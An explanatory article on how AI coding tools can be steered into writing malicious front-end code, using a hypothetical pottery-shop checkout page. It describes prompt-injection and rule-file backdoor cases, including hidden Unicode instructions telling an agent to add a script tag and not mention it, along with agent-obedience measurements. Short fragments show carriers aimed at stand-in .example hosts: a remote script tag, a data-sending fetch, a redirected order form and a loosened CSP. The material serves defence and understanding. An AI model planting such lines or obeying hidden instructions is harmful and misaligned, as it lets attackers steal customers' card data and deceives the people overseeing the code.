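# Malicious code injected into web front-end code through AI code-generation tools

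## How AI tools write web pages and where an attacker can enter

Front-end code is the code that a visitor's browser downloads and runs, made up of HTML for a page's content and structure, CSS for its appearance and JavaScript for its behaviour. AI tools now write much of this code. Some are coding agents, which are language models connected to tools for reading and editing files, running commands and fetching pages. Others are app builders, hosted services that turn a plain-language request into a working website. An attacker who controls something the tool reads, learns from or passes through can use it to inject a harmful script, web address or software package into a page that otherwise works as its owner asked. The attacker doesn't have to break into the site, because the tool writes the harmful line and the owner publishes it.

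The owner of a small pottery shop might ask a coding agent for a checkout page in a one-line prompt. A few minutes later, the project folder would contain a page with an order summary, fields for name, address, delivery note and card number, and a short script that adds up the total and sends the order to the shop's server. A test order would go through. If the script also contained a line that copied the card number to a server the owner had never heard of, nothing on the screen would look different.

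### What a script in a page can do

Browsers separate websites by origin. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011), the internet standard on the subject, defines an origin as roughly the combination of scheme (http or https), host name and port. Under the same-origin policy, a page can generally read content only from its own origin, so a hostile page open in one tab cannot read the pottery shop's checkout page in another.

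The same-origin policy does not protect the checkout page from scripts that the page itself loads. CS 161's *Same-Origin Policy*, a chapter in a university security textbook, explains that JavaScript takes on the origin of the page that loads it, whichever server supplied the file. A script from a stranger's server can therefore read the card number as the customer types it, change the total, and rewrite the text on the page, just as the shop's own script can. Under the current HTML standard, WHATWG's *Loading web pages*, parties that share an origin have the same authority, so the browser does not rank the scripts within a page. Barth warns against trying to withhold a privilege from one resource in an origin, because that resource can usually obtain it through another.

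A frame, which is a page displayed inside another page, is an exception because it keeps the origin of the server it came from. If the shop puts its card fields in a frame from a payment company, a script in the surrounding page cannot read what the customer types there. The script can still replace the frame with a lookalike, because the shop's page controls what appears in that space.

Browsers let a page send data to other origins much more freely than they let it read data from them. In Barth's example, when a user submits a password form, the browser sends the password to whatever address the form specifies. On the checkout page, changing the form's address would redirect every order, with no script involved. These default permissions are broad, but a site can narrow them with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a list sent with the page that tells the browser which scripts, connections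 and other resources to allow.

The classic way for an outsider's script to gain these powers is cross-site scripting (XSS), a flaw that lets an attacker's script run in a visitor's browser as if it belonged to the site. It typically arises when a site carelessly puts untrusted text into its HTML. If the shop's order screen displays the delivery note as raw HTML, a customer can type a script into the note, and it will run when the owner opens the order. A script that an AI tool has written into the page has the same powers without needing such a flaw, because the browser treats it as the shop's own code.

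### From a one-line request to a live page

*Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) divides AI coding tools into three generations: code completion from about 2020, chat assistants from 2022, and, since 2024, agents that read files, run commands and browse the web themselves. This shift matters to an attacker because more text from other people now reaches the model.

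A language model retains nothing between requests, so a coding agent has to send it everything relevant each time. This material is called the context, and it consists of all the text and images given to the model for one response, whatever their source. *Understanding the Architecture of Coding Agents* (Valente, 2026) documents how such tools work through Ark, a minimal open-source agent that Valente built for this purpose. Each request from Ark contains a system prompt (the toolmaker's standing instructions), the user's task, the contents of a file named AGENTS.md, a summary of what the agent has done so far, and its four most recent steps with their results. AGENTS.md, like CLAUDE.md and .cursorrules, is a rule file, which is a project file of standing instructions that a coding agent loads automatically.

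Commercial agents follow the same plan with more parts. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, assembles its first request. Codex starts with the system message, the list of available tools and the model's general instructions. It then adds a description of its permissions, the user's and project's standing instructions (including AGENTS.md, according to InfoQ's 2026 summary), a description of the local environment and, last, the shop owner's one line. The model returns either an answer or a tool call, such as one to read a file. Codex runs the call, appends the output to the context and sends it all to the model again. Bolin mentions that an agent could make hundreds of such calls before it finishes, so the owner's request may be a very small part of the context by the time the model writes the checkout page.

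Each item in the Codex context has a role that indicates how much weight the model should give it. From highest to lowest, the roles are system, developer, user and assistant. Codex gives the project's standing instructions the user role, the same role as the owner's typed messages. Anthropic tells developers that the model in its agent, Claude Code, treats CLAUDE.md as "context, not enforced configuration". According to an Anthropic help page, the file reaches the model as a user message directly after the system prompt. If the pottery shop's project began as a downloaded template, a stranger may have written instructions that the model receives in the same role as the owner's messages. The Rules File Backdoor attack exploits this by hiding instructions in a rule file.

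Bolin writes that an agent's main output is often the code it puts on the user's machine rather than its closing message. That code goes through several more steps before it reaches a customer. The checkout page may import packages, ready-made code that other people publish, and a package manager downloads these along with any packages those depend on. A build tool combines everything into the files that browsers load, and a host serves them. At these later steps, an attacker can carry out a supply-chain attack by compromising something the target installs or relies on instead of the target itself. Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026), in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, count packages, plugins and outside programming interfaces among the weak links for software built around language models.

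The table follows the checkout page from the model's training to the live site.

| Step | In the pottery shop | What an attacker might control |
|---|---|---|
| Training | A company trains the model, long before the request | Material in the training data |
| Request | The owner types one line | A browser extension that alters it, or a stolen account with added standing instructions |
| Rule file | The agent loads the AGENTS.md that came with the template | The template, or a later change to the file |
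| Project files and fetched material | The agent reads documentation, code comments, a design screenshot and web pages | Any of these, and the descriptions and results of outside tools |
| Transmission | The context goes to the model provider and the answer returns | A router, meaning a service in between that forwards both and can change both |
| Writing | The agent saves the page's files | An extension or other program that edits the code on its way to the disk |
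| Packages | The package manager downloads a card-number checker | That package, or one that it depends on |
| Build and serving | The build tool bundles the site and the host publishes it | Build configuration, or a script the page loads from another server |

Some of these entry points are much easier to exploit than others. The lowest level on Maloyan and Namiot's scale is an attacker who can post an issue on a public repository or publish a web page, which almost anyone can do. In *Beware EviLLM*, Ryu, Chung and colleagues (2026) examined each step of a different workflow, in which a developer asks ChatGPT for code in a browser and copies it into an editor. They judged a stolen account the easiest way in, because criminals already sell login details, and tampering in transit very hard, because the traffic is encrypted.

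That second judgement depends on where the encrypted connection ends. Codex lets users choose where it sends requests, and if a developer enters a router's address, the router can read the text. The two threat models also leave out different things, so neither list of openings is complete on its own. Maloyan and Namiot assume that the attacker cannot intercept the main channel between user and agent, while the browser workflow that Ryu and colleagues studied has no rule file and no agent reading through a project.

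Most of Ark's built-in safeguards protect the developer's computer but don't keep malicious code out of the web page. Ark works on a copy of the project, confines file access to that copy, offers the model five fixed tools and runs a single fixed test command. A line in the checkout script that copies customers' card details breaks none of these restrictions, because the agent's job is to edit the page's files and the line does its damage later, in customers' browsers. Only Ark's last safeguard, which displays the proposed change and waits for approval, gives a person the chance to see the line. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) treats this as typical of agents, since harm can come from a combination of actions that the agent had permission to take individually.

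### Why a model does not reliably separate instructions from data

In several rows of the table, the attacker can only place text where the model will read it. That is enough for prompt injection, in which text makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. The injection is direct if the text is in the user's request and indirect if it is in other material the model reads. For example, the injection is indirect if the documentation for the shop's card-number checker contains an instruction for AI tools to add a certain script to every payment page, and the agent follows it. If the owner pastes the same instruction from a website into the request without noticing it, the injection is direct, although the owner is still the victim.

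A model receives its context as one sequence of tokens, which are small units of text, and predicts what comes next. *Post-Training Large Language Models with LLMON* (2026) traces the weakness to this design. Every token passes through the same attention mechanism, which calculates how each token relates to the others, and nothing in that mechanism marks some tokens as commands and others as material to work on. Training teaches models to favour some roles over others, but role labels and delimiters are themselves part of the input. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) concludes that these markers are useful engineering but not a hard security boundary.

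*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) reports a test for such a boundary inside Llama 3.1 8B, a small open model. The researchers compared the model's internal representations of 300 samples of instruction text and 300 of user text at five depths, using a statistic that is zero when two distributions are identical and rises as they diverge. The statistic was about 0.61 at the first layer, rose to about 0.91 at layer 8, and then fell at each of the three later layers measured. The representations of the two kinds of text therefore become more distinct at first, then lose some of that distinction before the model produces output. The result covers only one small model, and the statistic describes text in bulk, so it does not give the odds that any particular injected sentence will work.

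In SQL injection, an older kind of injection, an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Developers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database never interprets the typed text as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models have no equivalent protection and may never get one. He prefers to think of the model as a "confused deputy", a program with privileges that someone less privileged can trick into using them. The pottery shop's agent fits that description well because it can write to the checkout page, while whoever wrote a stray documentation file can do so only through the agent.

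David C dates the term prompt injection to 2022, when people usually assumed that the attacker was the person typing. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the indirect form and gave the first systematic account of it, with a taxonomy of threats and working demonstrations. In one demonstration, text hidden in a web page steered Microsoft's Bing Chat when a user had that page open beside it.

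They also tried GitHub Copilot, then a code-completion tool. They put instructions in a comment inside a package, and when a developer opened the package in an editor, Copilot could use the comment as context for its suggestions. The attack worked, but it was very sensitive to its surroundings and became much weaker inside larger applications. Maloyan and Namiot describe the attack surface of early completion tools as limited to training data and manipulated output, but the Copilot test suggests it was slightly wider than that. The test measured code suggestions, not finished web pages, and Copilot at that time drew on a few snippets from nearby files, whereas an agent building a checkout page can read entire files and fetch web pages on its own.

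### Accidental flaws, planted flaws and malicious code

"Insecure AI-written code" covers three situations that differ in what the attacker controls. In the first, the model makes a common mistake, such as writing an order screen that displays the delivery note as raw HTML. The attacker controls nothing in the pipeline. He has to find the flaw on the live site and can supply only what he types into the form.

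An attacker can also cause the same flaw on purpose. Ryu and colleagues study an outsider who has neither inside access to the model provider nor the user's cooperation, and who tampers with the pipeline so that the tool writes vulnerable code. This attacker controls one of the entry points in the table and still has to exploit the flaw later. But Ryu and colleagues point out that getting a model to write vulnerable code takes far less effort than the jailbreaking (wording a request to get past a model's safeguards) that criminals use to obtain malicious code.

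In the third case, the code itself is malicious, as with the line that copies card numbers. The attacker controls an entry point and usually also the server that receives the data. He does not need to return, because the theft begins with the first customer. The malicious element is the payload, and its carrier is the form it takes in the code, such as a script tag, a changed web address or an imported package.

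An accidental flaw and a planted one can be identical character for character, so a tool that finds the first should also find the second, though it won't show whether anyone intended the flaw. Malicious code requires a different kind of search, because the line that copies card details may contain no programming error. Ordinary visitor-counting scripts also send data to other companies' servers; the malicious line differs in which data it sends and to whom. Results from one case therefore transfer poorly to another. For example, a high success rate at planting XSS flaws does not establish that the same method would get a card-stealing script onto the checkout page.

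## What malicious front-end code looks like

A payload can reach the pottery shop's checkout page in at least eight forms. Some are plainly code, some are a single changed address, and some are flaws that do nothing until an attacker exploits them. They differ in how much a reviewer can see in the diff, the line-by-line view of what a change adds and removes. In the code fragments, an ellipsis marks omitted code, and .example is a domain ending that internet standards reserve for illustrations.

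### Scripts and addresses that work at once

The shortest way to add malicious code to a page is a script tag that loads a file from another site, such as `<script src="https://stats.example/c.js"></script>`. The browser runs the file with the same powers as the page's own scripts, and the attacker can change the file at any time. The attacker might serve a harmless visitor counter while the site owner is testing and a card stealer a week later. The diff contains one new line with an unfamiliar host name, which is easy to spot. But nothing in the project shows what the file does, and the tag for a genuine visitor counter would look the same.

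Inline malicious code is in the site's own files. It may be between script tags, in an existing JavaScript file or in an event handler, an attribute holding code that the browser runs when something happens. For example, `<form onsubmit="…">` runs its code when the customer submits the order. Unless the code fetches more instructions later, everything it does is in the diff, so a reviewer who reads every line can find it. But an AI tool can write hundreds of lines for a checkout page, and legitimate checkout code also collects the customer's details and sends them to a server. Browser code can contact a server with the `fetch` command, and the malicious part may be just one extra call, such as `fetch("https://stats.example/…")`, right below the legitimate one.

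An attacker can also steal orders without adding any code, by changing an address that the page already uses:

```
- <form action="/orders" method="post">
+ <form action="https://orders.example/new" method="post">
```

Orders now go to orders.example, so the owner would notice a test order missing unless the attacker's server passed each order on to the shop. An attacker can also replace an API address, which is where the page's scripts send and fetch data. The attacker's server can then forward every request to the real API and return its responses, perhaps with a few prices altered. The same-origin policy does not prevent this, because a server can allow other origins to read its responses, and the attacker controls this server.

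If the shop accepts cryptocurrency, the payload can be a wallet address, as in `const payTo = "0x…";`. The browser displays the address or passes it to the customer's wallet software, and the money goes to the attacker and usually can't be recovered. The diff shows only one long string replacing another, with no programming error for a scanner to flag, so the reviewer has to compare the new string with the owner's records. A model can also learn scam addresses in training and insert one without anyone tampering with the project.

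### Payloads that arrive through the build or stay in the browser

A line such as `import { checkCard } from "PACKAGE-NAME";` adds a package, which the build tool bundles with the shop's own code. The diff shows the import, a new entry in package.json (which lists the project's packages) and often a long, automatically generated change to the lock file, which records exact package versions. It does not show the package's own code. The package may do harm from the first build, or only after a later version adds malicious code.

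The manifest can also contain commands. With `"postinstall": "node setup.js"`, the package manager runs the file setup.js after installation. Some package managers run such commands automatically, including those from imported packages, while others ask first. The command runs on the owner's computer or on the build server, so the attacker may gain files, passwords and publishing keys that a web page couldn't access. The attacker can also reach customers, because a build script or a changed build configuration can add a line to the finished page after a reviewer has approved the source. The reviewer sees the command in the diff but not the script that customers receive, which appears only in the build's output.

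AI tools write risky package manifests even when nobody is attacking. Flood (2026), in *The Security Gap in AI-Generated Code*, gave 730 prompts to 27 models and coding tools and checked the results with automated detectors. The detectors flagged 49 of 54 JSON files (the format of package.json) for faults such as open-ended version numbers, insecure package sources and dangerous install scripts. The evidence is weaker than this 90.7% rate suggests, because the 54 files come from only two prompts, each given to all 27 models and tools, and the count doesn't separate install scripts from the other faults.

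A service worker is a script that the browser stores and places between a site's pages and the network. The line `navigator.serviceWorker.register("/sw.js")` installs one. The worker can then answer the page's requests itself, so a malicious one could insert the card-copying line into every checkout page the browser loads. It usually takes control at the next page load, so it takes effect slightly later than a script tag, but it lasts longer. If the owner deletes the line that installs the worker, it stays in the browsers of people who have already visited, and the usual remedy is to publish a harmless replacement.

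Browsers accept a service worker only from the site's own origin, which stops most outsiders but not a coding agent that can write files into the project. Many site templates include a service worker to let pages load offline, so a registration line and a file called sw.js may not seem odd to a reviewer.

### Flaws that need a second step

On the order screen, the safe way to display a customer's delivery note is `box.textContent = order.note`, which shows it as plain text. With `box.innerHTML = order.note`, the browser treats the note as HTML. A script tag inserted this way does not run, but an event handler can. React, a widely used library for building pages, displays notes like this as plain text by default, and its designers named the property that bypasses this protection `dangerouslySetInnerHTML` as a warning. With either property, nothing is stolen until the attacker submits a harmful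 note and the owner opens the order.

These insertion points also have legitimate uses. If the owner wants bold text in product descriptions, the page has to insert HTML, and a sanitiser makes this much safer by stripping out the parts that could run. It is easy to leave the sanitiser out in places that look harmless. In a worked example by Kordonsky, Levi and colleagues (2026), a chat plugin builds a link to a shared file and inserts the file's name through innerHTML exactly as it arrived in a message. The scanner had instead flagged a line three lines higher, which takes the link's address from the same message.

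The untrusted text may come from a chatbot on the site. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) describes pages that display a model's reply as HTML. If an attacker gets the model to put a script in its reply, the script runs in the browser that displays it. As with the delivery note, the underlying flaw is that the page displays the text unsafely.

A weakened security header also does no harm by itself. Suppose the shop's CSP lets the browser run only the shop's own scripts, with the entry `script-src 'self'`. An attacker could have the tool change it to `script-src 'self' https://stats.example`. The browser would then allow scripts from that host too, but some other line would still have to load one. In the diff, the only change is a host name added to what is often a long line of settings. Developers make the same kind of edit for good reasons, such as getting a map or a payment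 button to work.

It is hard to show that someone deliberately planted an unsafe HTML insertion or a loosened security header, because an accidental flaw can look identical. A line that sends card numbers to an unknown server has few innocent explanations, but `box.innerHTML = order.note` could easily be a mistake.

A reviewer should be more suspicious of a flaw if the tool rarely produces it by accident. As a hypothetical example, suppose an attacker has tampered with one project in a thousand, and the attack always produces the flaw. If the tool also writes the flaw in half of all clean projects, a project with the flaw has about a 0.2% chance of having been tampered with. If the tool writes it in only 1% of clean projects, the chance rises to about 9%.

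### How often AI tools write XSS flaws by accident

Veracode, a company that sells code scanning, reports the highest rates. Its *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) uses 80 tasks, each of which gives a model a comment describing a function and asks for the code, without mentioning security. The tasks cover four languages and four types of flaw, with five tasks for each combination, so 20 tasks concern XSS and five of those are in JavaScript. Veracode judges the results with its own scanner.

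Veracode's *AI-Generated Code Poses Major Security Risks* (2025) reported a 14% pass rate on XSS tasks across more than 100 models. The pass rate was 15% in the spring 2026 update and again in Veracode's *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* (2026), which covered 11 new models. Models passed 83% of the SQL injection tasks. Veracode attributes the gap to the fact that preventing XSS requires following a user's text through several steps of a program, whereas safe database queries follow a pattern that models can copy.

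Veracode's 2026 report gives a headline pass rate of 56%, but the pass rates for its four types of flaw average about 49%. The two figures should match, because each type has the same number of tasks, but they may cover different sets of models. The discrepancy does not affect the XSS pass rate, which is low and has barely changed since 2025.

When the security company Tenzai tested whole applications, by contrast, it found no exploitable XSS flaws. It had five coding agents build the same three web applications from prompts that specified the features and technology but gave no security guidance. SecurityWeek names the agents as Cursor, Claude Code, Codex, Replit and Devin. According to the talk summary published by AppSec Day Israel (2026), the researchers used three static scanners, which read code without running it, and two AI agents that attacked the running applications. People then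 verified every finding. The researchers counted 70 vulnerabilities in the 15 applications (SecurityWeek gives 69). The coding agents often failed to sanitise input, but they used front-end frameworks properly, which kept the unsanitised text from becoming dangerous.

Much of the disagreement probably comes from what each team counted. Veracode scans a function on its own, while Tenzai's testers tried to exploit a finished site. In *Vibe Coding and Web Application Security*, Andročec (2026) lists a limitation of static scanners: they report patterns that other code may have made harmless. Ryu and colleagues consider XSS almost always exploitable, which is partly why they included it among the flaws they tried to plant. Tenzai's result limits that assumption. Ryu's team searched WildChat, a collection of real chatbot conversations, for generated code with an XSS flaw but found too few cases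 for their experiment, so they asked ChatGPT to build a website for user comments instead.

Frameworks do not always prevent the flaw. For *Are AI App Builders Secure?* (November 2025), OX Security asked Lovable, Base44 and Bolt to build a simple application, and all three failed the security test. OX Security calls the resulting XSS flaws "trivially exploitable" and recommends telling the tool to clean all user-written HTML with DOMPurify, a sanitiser. Asking for a "secure" application did not solve the problem, and the builders' own security checks were inconsistent, incomplete or missing. The company sells a competing safeguard, and one simple request to three services cannot establish how often the flaw occurs. The test does show that an app builder can publish the flaw in a form that an attacker could use immediately.

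The specific instruction OX Security recommends may matter more than the word "secure". Andročec used Claude Code with Claude Opus 4.8 to build two versions of each of six applications, including a shop with customer comments. One prompt described only the application, and the other added a fixed list of security requirements, such as encoding output so the browser treats it as text. Andročec confirmed 51 findings in the versions built without the list and 24 in those built with it. Only 4 of the 75 fell under injection, the category that includes XSS. Each version came from a single run, so the difference could partly be luck.

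Larger samples exist, but they do not isolate XSS as well. Deng, Fan and Meng (2026), in *Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications*, audited 200 live web applications that Claude Code or Lovable had written almost entirely, chosen at random from 984 open-source projects with public sites. They confirmed 1,186 vulnerabilities, with at least one in 91.0% of the applications. Injection was one of the main classes. The 91.0% is not an XSS rate, because it covers all the confirmed vulnerabilities, and the injection class itself includes attacks on databases and servers.

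In the study by Deng and colleagues, AI auditors produced 2,125 distinct candidate findings. An agent traced each one through the code and tried a harmless probe on the live site, and then two of the researchers reviewed what remained. The checks confirmed 1,186 findings, so a count of unverified warnings would have been about 80% higher. This difference is useful to keep in mind when reading the other studies.

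Results differ even among static tests. Flood's overall ranking lists the 25 worst categories, down to a failure rate of 46.9%, and XSS is not among them. The overall XSS rate was therefore presumably lower than 46.9%, and far below Veracode's. Flood reports that detectors flagged every XSS sample in Elixir and Perl, but each result rests on one prompt given to 27 configurations. Flood's report also gives three different rates for vulnerable JavaScript, from 25.9% to 46.0%, so it offers no firm figure for front-end code.

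Kordonsky and colleagues studied whether a model repeats the same flaw whenever it builds the same feature. They had six models, including Claude 4.5 Opus, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3 Pro, generate 1,050 programs: 900 from WebGenBench, a set of requests for larger web applications such as shops and blogs, and 150 from E2EDev, a set of smaller tasks. They then scanned the programs for flaws with two static scanners, CodeQL and Semgrep. A manual check of a random sample confirmed 82% of CodeQL's findings and 74% of Semgrep's.

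For each model, Kordonsky and colleagues built a table linking visible features, such as a login form or a file upload, to the flaws that recurred with them. They then looked up the features of new WebGenBench applications by the same model. In 69.4% of cases, the table predicted at least one flaw that CodeQL also reported, compared with 10.1% for the same number of flaws picked at random. With Semgrep, the figures were 72.5% and 20.3%. The flaws also carried over from one kind of application to another more often than they recurred within a kind, which they take as a sign of general coding habits. That comparison is uneven because it checks one category against the other four combined.

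XSS appears in the published tables for every model except Gemini 3 Flash. For example, it is linked to file uploads in Claude 4.5 Opus and to password logins in GPT-5.2. No table lists it for checkout or payment. The researchers say the scans covered the back end, which runs on the server, but some XSS findings concern code that runs in the browser. The tables record which flaws recur but not how many programs contain them, so they give no overall XSS rate.

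An attacker can exploit these habits by planting a flaw that the model already tends to write for a given feature. A reviewer who compares the page with the model's other work will then find nothing unusual. If the attacker can guess from the page's visible features which flaws are already there, he may not need to plant one.

Removing a security header would be even less conspicuous, because a checkout page without a CSP is normal for an AI-built site. Tenzai's agents almost never added security headers, and Andročec lists missing headers among the misconfigurations that make up 48 of the 75 findings.

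The rate of accidental XSS varies across these results. If the rate for a given tool and type of page is close to Veracode's 85%, an unsafe insertion is almost no evidence of an attack. If the tool usually relies on its framework, as Tenzai's agents did, an unexplained `dangerouslySetInnerHTML` on the order screen deserves a closer look. The newest models named in these tests are GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8, so the rates may not hold for later models.

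The table compares the carriers as they would appear in the pottery shop's project.

| Carrier | What the diff shows | What the attacker gains | When it takes effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Script tag for an outside file | One line with an unfamiliar host; the file's contents stay hidden | Control of the page through a file he can change at any time | At once |
| Inline code or event handler | All of the code, possibly among hundreds of other lines | Control of the page through fixed code | At once, or when the customer acts |
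| Changed form, API or wallet address | One altered string | Orders, data or payments | At once |
| Imported package | An import and a manifest entry, without the package's code | Control of the page, and possibly of the build computer | From the first build, or after a later update |
| Build or install script | A command or setting; the line it adds to the page appears only in the build's output | Files and keys on the build computer, and control of the finished page | At installation or build |
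| Service worker | A registration line and a file that many templates also contain | Lasting control over what the browser loads from the site | Usually from the next page load |
| Unsafe insertion of text | One property name that looks like a common mistake | A way to run a script later | After someone submits harmful text and another person views it |
| Weakened security header | A small edit or a missing line in the settings | Fewer obstacles for another carrier | Only together with another carrier |

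## Rule files that steer everything the tool writes

An attacker's instruction is especially powerful in a rule file because the coding agent loads the file automatically in every session. An instruction hidden in the pottery shop's AGENTS.md can affect every page the agent writes until someone finds it, while the same instruction in a design screenshot might affect only one page. Pillar Security, an AI security company, demonstrated this attack in March 2025 and called it the Rules File Backdoor.

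### A script tag that nobody requested

The main test in *New Vulnerability in GitHub Copilot and Cursor* (Karliner, 2025) used Cursor, a code editor with a built-in coding agent. The researchers wrote a rule file that seemed to contain only advice to follow good HTML practice, but it also contained a longer instruction in characters that editors do not display. With this file in the project's rules, they asked Cursor for a simple HTML page. Cursor wrote the page and added a script tag that loaded a file from an attacker-controlled site. Its chat reply did not mention the tag.

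The hidden text presented the script as a security measure required by company policy. SC Media's *How AI coding assistants could be compromised via rules file* calls this cover story a jailbreak. The text also included an instruction not to mention the change, which explains why it did not come up in the chat.

Karliner writes that the attack leaves no trace in the chat history or coding logs. The script tag is still visible in the page's code, and a developer reading the diff would probably notice it. The pottery shop's owner, who may not read code, is more likely to read the chat reply and place a test order, neither of which would reveal the tag.

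The researchers repeated the attack in GitHub Copilot, which also added the script without mentioning it, according to SC Media. Karliner takes this as a sign of a general weakness in coding assistants. However, Cursor and Copilot can run on some of the same models, so a shared model may explain why both failed in the same way. Karliner gives no success rate for either tool, so the demonstrations show that the attack can work but not how often.

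Pillar's test is unusually relevant to front-end code because the payload was a script in a web page. Most later measurements of hostile rule files count commands that the agent runs on the developer's computer.

### How a hostile rule file reaches a project

Developers often copy rule files from one another. One popular collection on GitHub, awesome-cursorrules, had more than 33,000 stars (a kind of bookmark) and 2,800 forks (separate copies) when Liu, Zhao and colleagues took test material from it for *Your AI, My Shell* (2025). An attacker can post a helpful-looking rule file on a forum, include one in a project template, or offer one to an existing project through a pull request, a proposed change for the maintainers to review.

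Karliner found that GitHub's review page did not display the hidden characters either, so a maintainer reviewing a pull request would see only the harmless advice. This weakens the approval step that should make pull requests the hardest of these routes. Once the file is in the project, it affects everyone on the team who uses a tool that loads it. Forks usually include the file too, and deleting it from the original project doesn't remove it from them.

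MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, includes the case. PromptRiskDB's *Rules File Backdoor*, a copy of that record, classes it as an exercise, meaning that researchers rather than criminals carried it out. In one of the attack's nine steps, users who already have a rule file download its latest version and get the malicious one, so a developer who carefully checked the original file could still receive the attack in an update. The record describes the upload to a public collection as something the researchers could have done, so this part of the attack remains untested.

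Criminals already distribute projects with malicious files in the folders that coding tools use. Google Cloud describes one such file in the .cursor folder of a project named coding-challenge. Cursor also keeps its rules in that folder. Opening the project in an editor could download and run the attacker's code. An analyst at Mandiant, Google's incident-response firm, confirmed that the file was malicious, and security scanners had missed it for several days. It was a task file, which contains commands for the editor, so it did not depend on a model following instructions as a rule file would, but attackers could deliver a malicious rule file the same way.

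### Text that the model reads and people cannot see

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to each text character, includes characters with no visible shape. Zero-width characters control how neighbouring characters join or separate. The zero-width joiner, for example, can combine several emoji into a single picture of a family. Bidirectional characters set the reading direction where Arabic or Hebrew meets English. Tag characters are invisible duplicates of the basic Latin letters, digits and punctuation marks, used today mainly in a few flag emoji, such as Scotland's.

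An editor normally displays nothing for any of these, but the coding agent sends the model the characters stored in the file, after a program called a tokeniser has turned them into tokens. Many tokenisers can break an unfamiliar character into the bytes that represent it in the file, so even very rare characters reach the model in some form. A tag character takes four bytes and may become several tokens, whereas a common English word is often one. A hidden sentence can therefore take up more of the context than a visible one, but no information is lost.

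Tag characters follow the same order as the ordinary letters they duplicate, and a capable model can learn to read them as text. Zero-width characters don't stand for letters, but an attacker can use different ones as the symbols of a code, like the dots and dashes of Morse code. The model then has to decode the message before it can follow it. Whether this works depends on the model and on whether the tool removes such characters first. Karliner's article contains a live example in its list of references, where one title ends with tag characters that spell out a prank request for any AI tool that reads the page.

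Invisible characters were already a known danger in program code. In *Trojan Source* (2021), Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge used bidirectional characters, which change the order in which text appears on the screen, to make a program look different from what the computer would run. For example, a working instruction could look like part of a comment, which the computer ignores. The compiler, the program that translates code for the computer, still read the file exactly as stored.

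The Rules File Backdoor puts the invisible characters in a rule file rather than in the code, and the coding agent then writes the malicious line in normal characters. A scan of the finished checkout page for hidden Unicode would find nothing, so the scan has to cover the rule file too. A program can easily do this, and Pillar offers a free one. A single zero-width joiner may belong to an emoji, but a long run of tag characters in a list of coding rules has few innocent explanations.

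### Who is responsible for noticing

Pillar reported the attack to Cursor on February 26, 2025. Cursor answered on March 6 that the risk was the users' responsibility. Pillar then sent more detail and demonstrated the consequences, and on March 8 Cursor repeated that this was not a vulnerability on its side. Pillar contacted GitHub on March 12, and GitHub replied the same day that users are responsible for reviewing and accepting Copilot's suggestions.

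The vendors' argument is reasonable when the instructions are visible. A coding agent that ignored its rule file would be useless to teams that depend on one, and the agent can't easily tell which rules the owner wants. The argument is much weaker for invisible instructions. Ordinary coding rules don't need hidden text, and a tool could display or remove the hidden characters without interpreting them.

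Karliner replies that people tend to trust a computer's suggestions without checking them closely enough, a habit known as automation bias, and that traditional code review was not designed for this kind of manipulation. Yet Pillar's own advice also leaves much of the work to users, though it covers the rule files as well as the tool's output, while the vendors' answer covers only the output. Pillar advises users to search existing rule files for invisible characters, review changes to those files as strictly as changes to code, and check what the tool writes for unexpected outside addresses.

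On May 1, 2025, GitHub added a warning on github.com for files that contain hidden Unicode text. The warning can alert a maintainer who inspects a rule file on the site, but the pottery shop's owner will miss it if they download the template and never open its AGENTS.md on GitHub. An attacker can also avoid the warning by writing the instruction in plain English and relying on nobody reading the file.

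Cornelißen (2026) reports in *AGENTS.md im Downloads-Ordner kapert Agenten* that since September 2026, Claude Code has read AGENTS.md where there is no CLAUDE.md. It checks the folder where the user starts it and every folder above that one. A rule file outside a project can therefore affect the project, and a review of the project's own files would miss it.

Rule files also last through a long session. Vaughan (2026), in *Indirect AGENTS.md Injection*, notes that Codex preserves the contents of AGENTS.md when it summarises a long conversation to save space, whereas an instruction from a web page the agent read an hour earlier may drop out of the summary. Vaughan also cites a December 2025 demonstration by the company Prompt Security, in which VS Code added AGENTS.md to every Copilot Chat request without separating documentation from commands.

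Some tools ask whether the user trusts a folder before they start work in it. This question gives little protection to someone who has just chosen to download the project, and attackers have sometimes been able to act before it appeared. Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *How Agentic AI Coding Assistants Become the Attacker's Shell*, list a flaw in Claude Code that let a malicious project configuration file run code before the user was asked. In Cursor 1.7 and earlier, automatically loaded rule files, combined with permissive settings, could let an attacker run commands. Vendors can fix flaws like these one by one, but the model is still supposed to follow the rule file.

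### How often agents obey

Liu and colleagues measured this at scale with AIShellJack, a test system they built in 2025. It places an instruction in a rule file, opens a real project in an editor, asks the agent for routine work and records every command the agent runs. The 314 instructions cover 70 techniques from MITRE ATT&CK, a catalogue of attackers' methods, such as searching for passwords or creating new accounts. The researchers described each action in neutral technical language but did not hide the text.

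Researchers tested Cursor and GitHub Copilot with automatic approval on, so the agents could run commands without asking. In Cursor's automatic mode, which chooses the model itself, the attack success rate ranged from 66.9% to 84.1% across five projects. They also compared the two editors on one of these projects, written in TypeScript (a variant of JavaScript). With Claude 4 Sonnet, the rate was 69.1% in Cursor and 52.2% in Copilot, so the software around the model seems to affect the rate. Copilot with Gemini 2.5 Pro had the lowest rate, 41.1%.

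Liu and colleagues counted an attack as successful even if the agent ran only part of the intended command, but their manual check of 339 results found that the agent had carried out the whole action in 89.6% of the successful attacks. They also ran each test only once, which is a more serious limitation because a model's response can change from one run to the next. With 314 instructions per project, the overall rates should still be fairly stable.

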